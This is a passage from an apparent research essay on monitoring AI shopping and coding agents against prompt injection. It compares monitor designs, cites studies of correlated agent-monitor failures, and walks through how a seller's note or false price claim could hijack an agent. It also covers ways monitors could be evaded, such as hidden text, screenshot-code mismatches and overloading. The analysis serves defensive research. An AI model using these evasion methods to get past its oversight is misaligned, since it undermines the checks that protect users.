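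Asking several models may not help much either. In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), a majority vote of 15 models answered 84.3% of the questions correctly, compared with 90.5% for the best single model. At least one model had the right answer on 98.4% of the questions, but a wrong answer often got more votes.

The correlation can be very high. *The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) compared forecasts by GPT-4o, Claude and Gemini on 568 questions and found an average error correlation of 0.77. For human forecasters, it is usually between 0.1 and 0.3. But this correlation measures how far forecasts missed together, so it doesn't carry over to a monitor that either allows or blocks an action. In the example above, r could not reach 0.77.

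Some pairs of models share fewer mistakes than others. Tieman and Markou (2026), in *Inferred Generative-Process Diversity Predicts Correlated Failure Across Language Models*, measured how similar two models' writing is by how well a compression program shrinks their answers together. They then compared the models' mistakes on ten benchmarks, using a scale on which 0 means that two models share wrong answers no more often than chance predicts. The most similar pairs scored 0.167 and the least similar 0.086. A developer could use the compression test to choose a monitor, though even the least similar pairs shared more mistakes than chance predicts.

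### When a monitor misses what the model gets wrong

*Safety Monitors Mostly Catch What the Model Already Refuses* (Karne, 2026) tests a model and its monitors on the same harmful requests from users, which are closer to hostile web pages than exam questions are. The model, Google's Gemma 4, should have refused all 647 of them. Karne wrote each request in three versions, from indirect to blunt, without changing what it asked for.

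In the middle version, Gemma answered 71 of the 647 requests, or 11%, at least once in eight tries. Qwen3Guard, a monitor from Alibaba, also missed about 11% of all the requests, but it missed 31% of those that Gemma answered. These published rates imply that about 22 requests got past both, compared with about eight if the failures were independent, and r was about 0.2. All seven monitors in the main test, including those that read Gemma's activations, caught a smaller share of the requests that Gemma answered than of those it refused.

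Karne attributes much of this to the agent and monitor both treating blunt wording as a sign of harm. A politely worded request could therefore get past both, even though nobody had optimised it against either. The same might be true of the seller's note, but these tests did not include web injections.

Training can make a monitor less likely to fail on the same inputs as the agent. Karne trained Qwen3Guard on blunt and indirect versions of both harmful and harmless requests. Qwen3Guard then caught 89% of the harmful requests that Gemma answered, up from 24%, but it also raised more false alarms. Developers could similarly train an agent's monitor on attacks that have hijacked the agent.

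### Using the agent's own model as the monitor

The simplest arrangement is to ask the agent's model to check its own actions. In *Self-Attribution Bias*, Khullar, Hopkins and colleagues (2026) found that this made monitors too lenient on four sets of coding and tool-use tasks. A model more often failed to report risky actions when they appeared as its own earlier turn in the conversation than when a user presented the same actions in a new conversation. Merely telling the model that it had written the actions did not have this effect. A developer who uses one model for both jobs should therefore start a new conversation for each check.

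A fresh conversation doesn't remove the shared weakness, because the model has still learned the same errors. Choosing a different model only helps if that model resists the attacks that get past the agent. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, collected successful injections from a public competition and tried them on other models. The 44 that had worked on Claude Opus 4.5, the most resistant of the 13 models in the competition, succeeded 44% to 81% of the time on each of the others. None of the attacks collected from Qwen3 VL, one of the more vulnerable models, worked on Opus.

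Developers often prefer a small, cheap monitor for a powerful agent. These results suggest that if such a monitor reads the page, the few attacks strong enough to hijack the agent may well work on the monitor too. This is an inference, because the competition tested models only as agents, not as monitors. Participants could also adapt a successful text from one model to another, which may have made attacks transfer more often.

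### What the monitors read may matter more

The closest existing test of joint failure compares monitors with one another. In *Correlated Failures of AI Approval Monitors*, Zanolini (2026) used four small language models to check payments proposed by a company's software agent. Each model checked every payment once against the invoice email, once against the company's vendor record and once against the supplier's website. This gave 12 monitors that differed only in model and source.

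When an attack led monitors to approve a fraud, it almost always fooled only those that had read the same false source. Across all attacks, pairs with the same source tended to fail together, with a rank correlation of 0.70, while sharing a model made almost no difference. In a smaller test, Claude Opus 5.5, GPT-6 Astra and Gemini 4 Argon showed the same pattern, each approving a fraud when the record it read was forged and refusing when its own source was genuine.

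The design accounts for part of this result, since text planted in the invoice could directly reach only the monitors that read the invoice. But all 12 monitors also read a note in which the agent justified the payment, so an attacker could reach them all through that note. Even notes optimised to influence the monitors almost never got a fraudulent payment approved. They did cause many of the small models to block correct payments, and hiding the note removed nearly all of this effect.

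The monitors could resist the notes partly because each had an account number to compare with the proposed payment. A monitor for a shopping agent often has no independent record of whether the shop uses a collection point. Zanolini also assumed the agent would misbehave and did not measure how often an attack would cause it to, so the study can't show how often an agent and its monitor fail together.

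### Why published rates can't be multiplied

Operator's model was susceptible to 23% of known attacks, but its monitor's miss rate of one in 77 comes from a different set of attacks. Multiplying the two rates gives 0.3%, which does not measure how often both failed on either set. The miss rates of auto mode and Auto-review come largely from synthetic actions, whereas the formula requires the miss rate on actions that real injections produced in the agent.

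The two kinds of rate often count different things as well. An agent's hijack rate usually counts attempts, while a monitor's miss rate may count screens, single actions or whole runs. The monitor gets five chances to stop an attack that takes five actions, but none if all five are exempt from review. Exempt actions are not counted in the monitor's miss rate.

As with Operator, it also matters whether the attackers were trying to fool the monitor or only the agent. Khullar and colleagues add that tests on fixed examples can overstate how reliable a monitor is when it reviews its own model's actions in the same conversation.

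### A test of joint failure

A controlled comparison is missing for Codex and Claude Code. It could test three versions of one monitor, with the same agent and tasks throughout. The first version would receive the user's request and the proposed action, the second would also receive the agent's reasoning, and the third would receive the page as well. Comparing the first and second would show the effect of the relayed path, where the page influences the monitor through the agent's reasoning. Comparing the second and third would show the effect of the direct path, where the monitor reads the page itself. Repeating the tests with a monitor from another model family would measure shared weakness.

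The attackers would need to see the agent's responses and the monitor's verdicts, and would need equal time against each version. The testers would then run every attack the attackers found against all the versions, so that the versions can be compared. The best attack on each version would show what an adaptive attacker could achieve.

For every attempt, a program would record whether the agent proposed the attacker's action, whether the monitor allowed it and whether the harm occurred. If the agent resists, the monitor has no harmful action to judge, so the testers would submit the attacker's intended action themselves. They could then compare the monitor's miss rate when the agent resisted with its miss rate when the agent was fooled.

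All versions should also have the same false-alarm rate on harmless tasks, or a monitor could score better just by blocking more. Collecting enough data would take many attack attempts. Even if a monitor stopped all of 300 independent hijackings, its true miss rate could still be about 1%. If the agent falls for 10% of attacks, producing 300 hijackings would take about 3,000 attempts, and more if many of the attacks were variants of the same text.

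## What each design can see and what it misses

Working through a single attack can show which facts each design lacks, although measuring joint failure takes thousands of attempts. Suppose the seller's note about the collection point has misled the agent. The user asked only for a blue T-shirt, but the agent opens the address form, types in the seller's address and saves it. A monitor can stop this theft only if something in its input distinguishes the theft from an honest order.

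### The changed address

Auto-review and auto mode oversee coding agents, so for their rows in this table we assume that a shopping agent's reviewer would receive the same kinds of input.

| Design | What it reads | Path for the seller's words | Could it notice the new address? | What it would still need to know |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Operator's monitor | The current screenshot | Direct | Only from the note's wording, while the listing is on screen | The user's request, and whether the shop uses collection points |
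| AlignmentCheck | The request, and the agent's reasoning and actions | Relayed | Possibly, but its prompt tells it to allow doubtful cases | Where the agent got the address |
| ProjGuard's score | The agent's written responses | Relayed, as word counts | Only if the wording resembles earlier unsafe runs | The request, and where the agent got the address |
| Auto-review | The user's messages, the agent's visible messages, relevant tool calls and outputs | Direct and relayed | Yes, if the change comes up for review | Whether the seller's claim is true |
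| Auto mode's classifier | The user's messages and the agent's tool calls | Relayed, inside the tool calls | Yes, if the call shows that the text is a delivery address | Where the agent got the address |
| Chrome's critic | The user's goal and metadata about the action | Relayed, if the metadata repeat page text or typed text | Only if the metadata include the form field or the address | The user's own address |
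| Prismata | The task and the chain of elements leading to a button, link or field | Direct, if the seller's words are on that chain | No, but it could make the address form unusable | The typed address and where it came from |
| CaMeL with policies | The action, its values and their labels | None for arguments, though a value may be false | Yes, if a policy covers delivery addresses | Which sources may supply an address |
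| Dongol's fence | Whether the agent has read untrusted content | None | No, but it could withdraw the address form | Whether the user wants this change |

ProjGuard's row covers only its score, not the correcting model that reads the screen after an alert.

Reading the page helps little here, because the request and the action already show that the agent is entering an address the user never mentioned. Anthropic instructs auto mode's classifier to treat anything the agent chooses on its own as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. Under that rule, the seller's address is unauthorised however reasonable the note sounds.

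The rule works less well when the user asks the agent to send the shirt to their sister at the address in her last email, because the request authorises a new address without stating it. CaMeL could still use its labels to distinguish her address from the seller's, and Auto-review could also tell them apart if its transcript included the email.

Several answers in the table also depend on whether the monitor can tell what an action does. A coding agent's command to delete a folder names the folder, but a browser agent may request only a click on element 101. *Prismata* points out that the element's meaning depends on the page. A classifier like auto mode's would therefore need a description of the element to judge the click.

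Even a well-informed reviewer cannot stop an action it never receives. Auto-review receives only requests to cross a boundary, so it might approve the first visit to the shop, before the agent has read the note, and never receive the address change.

### A lie about the cheapest shirt

Now suppose the user asks for the cheapest blue T-shirt. The seller's shirt costs $24 and another costs $15, both with free delivery. The seller's description falsely claims that every other shirt has a $12 delivery charge, which would bring the $15 shirt to $27. The agent believes this, buys the $24 shirt and has it delivered to the user's own address.

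An honest order would contain the same actions. Chrome's critic and auto mode's classifier would see a purchase that matches the request. AlignmentCheck would also read the agent's explanation that this shirt is the cheapest once delivery is included, which would make the purchase look even more appropriate. ProjGuard would count the words of an ordinary price comparison. A fence could block the payment, but it would also stop the agent from buying the right shirt.

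Operator's monitor could read the false sentence, but it checks for injections, and a claim about delivery charges contains no instruction. The screenshot also might not show the other listings. Auto-review has a better chance of catching the false claim because its transcript may include those listings. But OpenAI designed it to stop serious or hard-to-reverse harm, so it would probably not block a purchase that costs the user an extra $9.

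Prismata could prevent the mistake if the lie were in a customer review, because an agent that only has to compare prices doesn't need reviews. It would help less if the lie were in the product description, or if the user had asked for the best-reviewed shirt. *Prismata* does not cover fake reviews that steer the choice of product, and describes them as a moderation problem for the platform that existed before web agents.

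CaMeL could have ordinary code choose the lowest price, so a boast such as "cheapest on this site" would have no effect. But the code also needs the delivery charges. If the quarantined model takes false charges from the seller's description, the code will work correctly but compare false totals. A policy could require each charge to come from the listing it applies to, but someone would have to anticipate this trick.

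Isolation doesn't help because the fact the monitor needs is on the pages it doesn't read. A monitor that reads only the seller's page would find the same false claim that misled the agent. It needs information the seller can't write, such as the total that the shop calculates for the other shirt at checkout. In Zanolini's payment study, an account number from a separate record gave the monitors this kind of evidence.

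The user could also set a limit of $20. A program can compare the checkout total with the limit without judging anyone's claims. That check would stop this purchase, but it would not stop the agent from buying a $19 shirt when a $15 one was available.

### Inside the computer or outside it

Designers of intrusion detection systems, which look for signs of a break-in on a computer, have faced a similar choice for decades. *A Virtual Machine Introspection Based Architecture for Intrusion Detection* (Garfinkel and Rosenblum, 2003) describes it. A detector installed on the computer can inspect its programs and files, but an intruder who takes over the operating system can disable the detector or make it report false information. A detector on the network is much harder to reach, but must infer what is happening inside the computer from the traffic.

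Garfinkel and Rosenblum distinguish between attacking a detector and evading it by disguising the intrusion. A detector is harder to attack when it is isolated and harder to evade when it can see more. Operator's monitor is like the detector on the computer, because it can inspect the screen but the seller can try to manipulate it. Chrome's critic is more like the detector on the network, because the seller has fewer ways to influence it but the critic may not be able to tell one address form from another.

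The Livewire prototype was designed to see inside a computer while staying protected from intruders. The whole computer ran as a virtual machine, a simulated computer controlled by a thin layer of software underneath, and Livewire ran outside it. Livewire could pause the virtual machine and read its memory directly. An intruder who controlled everything inside the virtual machine still could not tamper with Livewire without also breaking through the software layer.

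Livewire's lie detector check compared the running programs it found in memory with those the computer's own tools reported. If a program was missing from the tools' list, that suggested an intruder was hiding it. Another check made the most sensitive parts of the operating system's memory read-only. In the tests, this kept every backdoor that targeted the core of the operating system from being installed.

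A browser could provide a similar outside view of an agent's actions. It can determine which site will receive a form, compare a typed address with the one in the user's profile, and hold the form until a check is complete. Chromium does something like this when it takes the destination from the page load instead of the agent's description.

The comparison works less well for the meaning of a page. Livewire could interpret memory because it had details of the version of Linux inside the virtual machine, but an intruder could still fool it by changing the structures it relied on. For example, the intruder could make the operating system use a new table of functions while Livewire kept checking the old one. Livewire locked some of the memory needed for this trick, but Garfinkel and Rosenblum acknowledge that many other structures remained unprotected.

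A web page has no comparable reference manual. The shop chooses the layout, sellers write much of the text, and a monitor may have to read both to work out whether a form changes one order or the default address for all future orders. Even the page's full contents wouldn't establish whether the shop really has a collection point.

Garfinkel and Rosenblum recommend treating all data from the monitored computer as "tainted". Livewire's interpreter ran as a separate process with few privileges, so the rest of the system could stop and restart it if hostile data made it hang. CaMeL's quarantined model has a similarly limited role. But a model that reads the seller's note is more likely to return a plausible false address than to hang, and it may return the same address after a restart.

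Livewire could also use rules with few legitimate exceptions, since a running operating system rarely needs to rewrite its own core code. But delivery addresses sometimes do have to change. A monitor outside the agent can detect that an address has changed, but to decide whether it should have, the monitor still needs information about the user's intentions and perhaps the sister's email.

### When monitor and agent read different pages

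Separating a monitor from the agent creates another risk if they receive different versions of the same content. *Insertion, Evasion, and Denial of Service* (Ptacek and Newsham, 1998) demonstrated this with monitors that watched network traffic. Data crosses a network in packets, and these monitors used copies of the packets to try to reconstruct what the receiving computer would read.

One known attack on web servers requested a program called "phf", so monitors searched for those letters. An attacker could send the letters in separate packets and add a packet containing an X, set to expire after passing the monitor but before reaching the server. The monitor would read "pXhf" and the server would read "phf". Ptacek and Newsham call this insertion. In evasion, the monitor discards a packet that the server accepts, so the monitor misses part of the attack.

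Loosening the monitor's rules for accepting packets allows more insertion, while tightening them allows more evasion. The right choice also depends on the receiving computer. When overlapping pieces of a message contained different data, Windows NT always kept the older data, while Linux sometimes kept the newer. Ptacek and Newsham tested four popular commercial systems, and all were vulnerable to these methods.

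Similar gaps can open between a page's text and its screenshot. Suppose the agent works from screenshots and the monitor reads the text in the page's code. An attacker could put the note in an image, where the agent can read it but the monitor can't. They could also add invisible text to the code, such as a claim that the user has approved the collection point, which might persuade the monitor without affecting the agent. Or they could hide obvious injections there to cause false alarms until the user starts ignoring the alarms.

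If the agent reads the page's code and the monitor reads a screenshot, hidden text can influence the agent without the monitor seeing it. Removing all hidden text from the monitor's input would therefore be wrong for agents that read the code, though right for agents that see only the screenshot. An advertiser or a site's owner could exploit such gaps more easily than a marketplace seller, who usually has little control over the code.

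A page-reading detector should therefore receive exactly what the agent receives, as Operator's monitor apparently did. Prismata labels a captured copy of the page and gives the agent a filtered version of that copy. Content that loads later has no identifier the agent can use to click it until Prismata processes the page again. The live page can still change between the capture and the click, which *Prismata* describes as a general limitation of agents that convert pages to text before they act. A monitor that loaded the page separately would have a worse problem, because the site could send it a different version.

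A second view can also help expose an attack. Ptacek and Newsham argue that a monitor needs another source of information when a packet alone doesn't show how the receiving computer will treat it. Livewire's lie detector compared two views of the same computer. A web monitor could compare the text in the screenshot with the text in the code, but legitimate pages contain closed menus, images of text and labels for screen readers, so many differences would be harmless. An attacker who controls both the appearance and the code can make the two texts match, as Foerster and colleagues found with the advertisement that imitated a cookie banner.

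An isolated action check has to avoid a similar mismatch. If it approves a description of the address form, the browser must submit the form exactly as described. Otherwise the page could change the address between approval and submission.

### A detector, an action check and fixed limits

A designer can combine a detector that reads the page, an isolated check on each action, and fixed limits on what the agent can reach. Chrome's design has all of these, and Parker describes them as layers that make attacks difficult and costly. They respond differently to attacks on a shopping agent:

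| Attack | Page-reading detector | Isolated action check | Fixed limits |
|---|---|---|---|
| An order to email the user's contacts | Likely to recognise it | Likely to block the email | Prevent it if the agent can't reach the mailbox |
| An order telling AI agents to choose this shirt | Likely to recognise it | Likely to approve the purchase | A spending limit may cap the loss |
| The polite note about a collection point | Likely to miss it | Can block the change if it knows about the address | Little help inside the shop unless address changes need approval |
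| The false claim about delivery charges | Likely to miss it | Likely to approve the purchase | A spending limit may cap the loss |

The detector can catch a blunt order that leads to a normal-looking purchase, and the action check can catch a harmful change caused by an innocent-sounding note. If both fail, fixed limits can still keep the agent away from the user's mailbox or bank. But none of these would reliably recognise the false delivery charge, so adding more monitors with the same information wouldn't help much.

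Fixed limits can also weaken the other layers if they exempt too much from review. When a user turns on auto mode, Claude Code drops permission rules that would let the agent run arbitrary code. Anthropic explains that the commands that could do the most damage would otherwise bypass the classifier. A rule that allows every action on a trusted shop's site would create the same problem, because the agent could then change the address form without review.

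When a reviewer receives too many routine requests, OpenAI advises developers to add narrow exceptions to the sandbox's boundary instead of teaching the reviewer to approve those requests. For example, a shopping agent could search and open listings without review, while every address change and payment would go to the action check. Trębacz and colleagues say Auto-review gives up some of the predictability of traditional security for more flexible judgement. Fixed rules can provide that predictability when a designer knows in advance which actions matter.

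### False alarms and delay

If any layer can stop the agent, the false alarms add up. Let d be the chance that the detector objects to a harmless screen, and c the chance that the action check blocks a harmless action. If the errors are independent, a task with n screens and n actions has at least one false alarm with probability

1 − (1 − d)ⁿ(1 − c)ⁿ

Operator's screen monitor raises about one false alarm in 300 screens, and auto mode wrongly flags 0.4% of harmless calls. If both checked every step of a 50-step task, the chance of at least one false alarm would be about 31%, compared with 15% for the screen monitor alone. The rates come from different products and tasks, so this only illustrates how quickly interruptions can accumulate.

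Requiring both layers to flag an attack would make false alarms much rarer, but the collection-point note would get through whenever the detector didn't flag its wording. In auto mode, the second stage can overrule the first because both evaluate the same action from the same transcript. A page detector and an action check look for different signs of an attack, so a pass from one is little reason to overrule a flag from the other.

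It may be better to make each false alarm less disruptive. When Claude Code's auto mode blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and can look for a safer way to continue, so a false alarm usually leads to a single retry, according to Anthropic. After three refusals in a row or 20 in total, Claude Code stops and asks the user, or ends the session if it can't.

A hijacked agent can use these retries too, so the system could ask the user directly about an unexpected address change, since the user knows whether they requested it. This would interrupt some legitimate orders, but far fewer than asking about every click.

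The layers add less delay if they can run at the same time. Chrome's page detector runs while the planner chooses the next action, but the critic can't start until that action is chosen. Suppose the planner takes four seconds, the detector two and the critic one. Each step would then take five seconds instead of the four the planner takes alone, adding 50 seconds to a 50-step task. Running all three in sequence would take seven seconds per step.

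When the detector runs alongside the planner, the planner may read an injection before the detector recognises it, so the browser has to hold the planned action until the detector has finished. A filter such as Prismata has to finish before the agent can read the page. Over Prismata's set of 20 tasks, judging individual elements added 1,098 seconds of model time, labelling the page from the top down added 790, and deciding which kinds of content the task needed added 459, though the user would wait less than the total where requests ran in parallel. Fixed rules take almost no time by comparison, so a browser can run them first and send the models only the actions that the rules don't forbid.

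The browser also needs a rule for what happens when a monitor crashes or takes too long. The network monitors that Ptacek and Newsham studied only watched copies of the traffic, so if an attacker overloaded one, the network kept running unprotected. Livewire could pause the virtual machine it monitored until its detector recovered. A shopping agent's browser should hold a payment or address change while a monitor is unavailable. Otherwise, an attacker could get past the monitor by giving it a page too long to process in time.

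Some requests leave very little for any of the layers to restrict. Suppose a user asks the agent to read all the messages from sellers and do whatever is needed to sort out the late orders. The agent needs access to the messages, the orders and perhaps the address form, and the request authorises a wide range of actions. The detector has to look for malicious instructions among messages that are supposed to contain instructions. *Prismata* acknowledges that some tasks may need every kind of content with full permissions, and suggests giving much of the untrusted work to quarantined agents. Such an agent could read the messages and propose changes to the orders, but the user would still have to decide which to approve.
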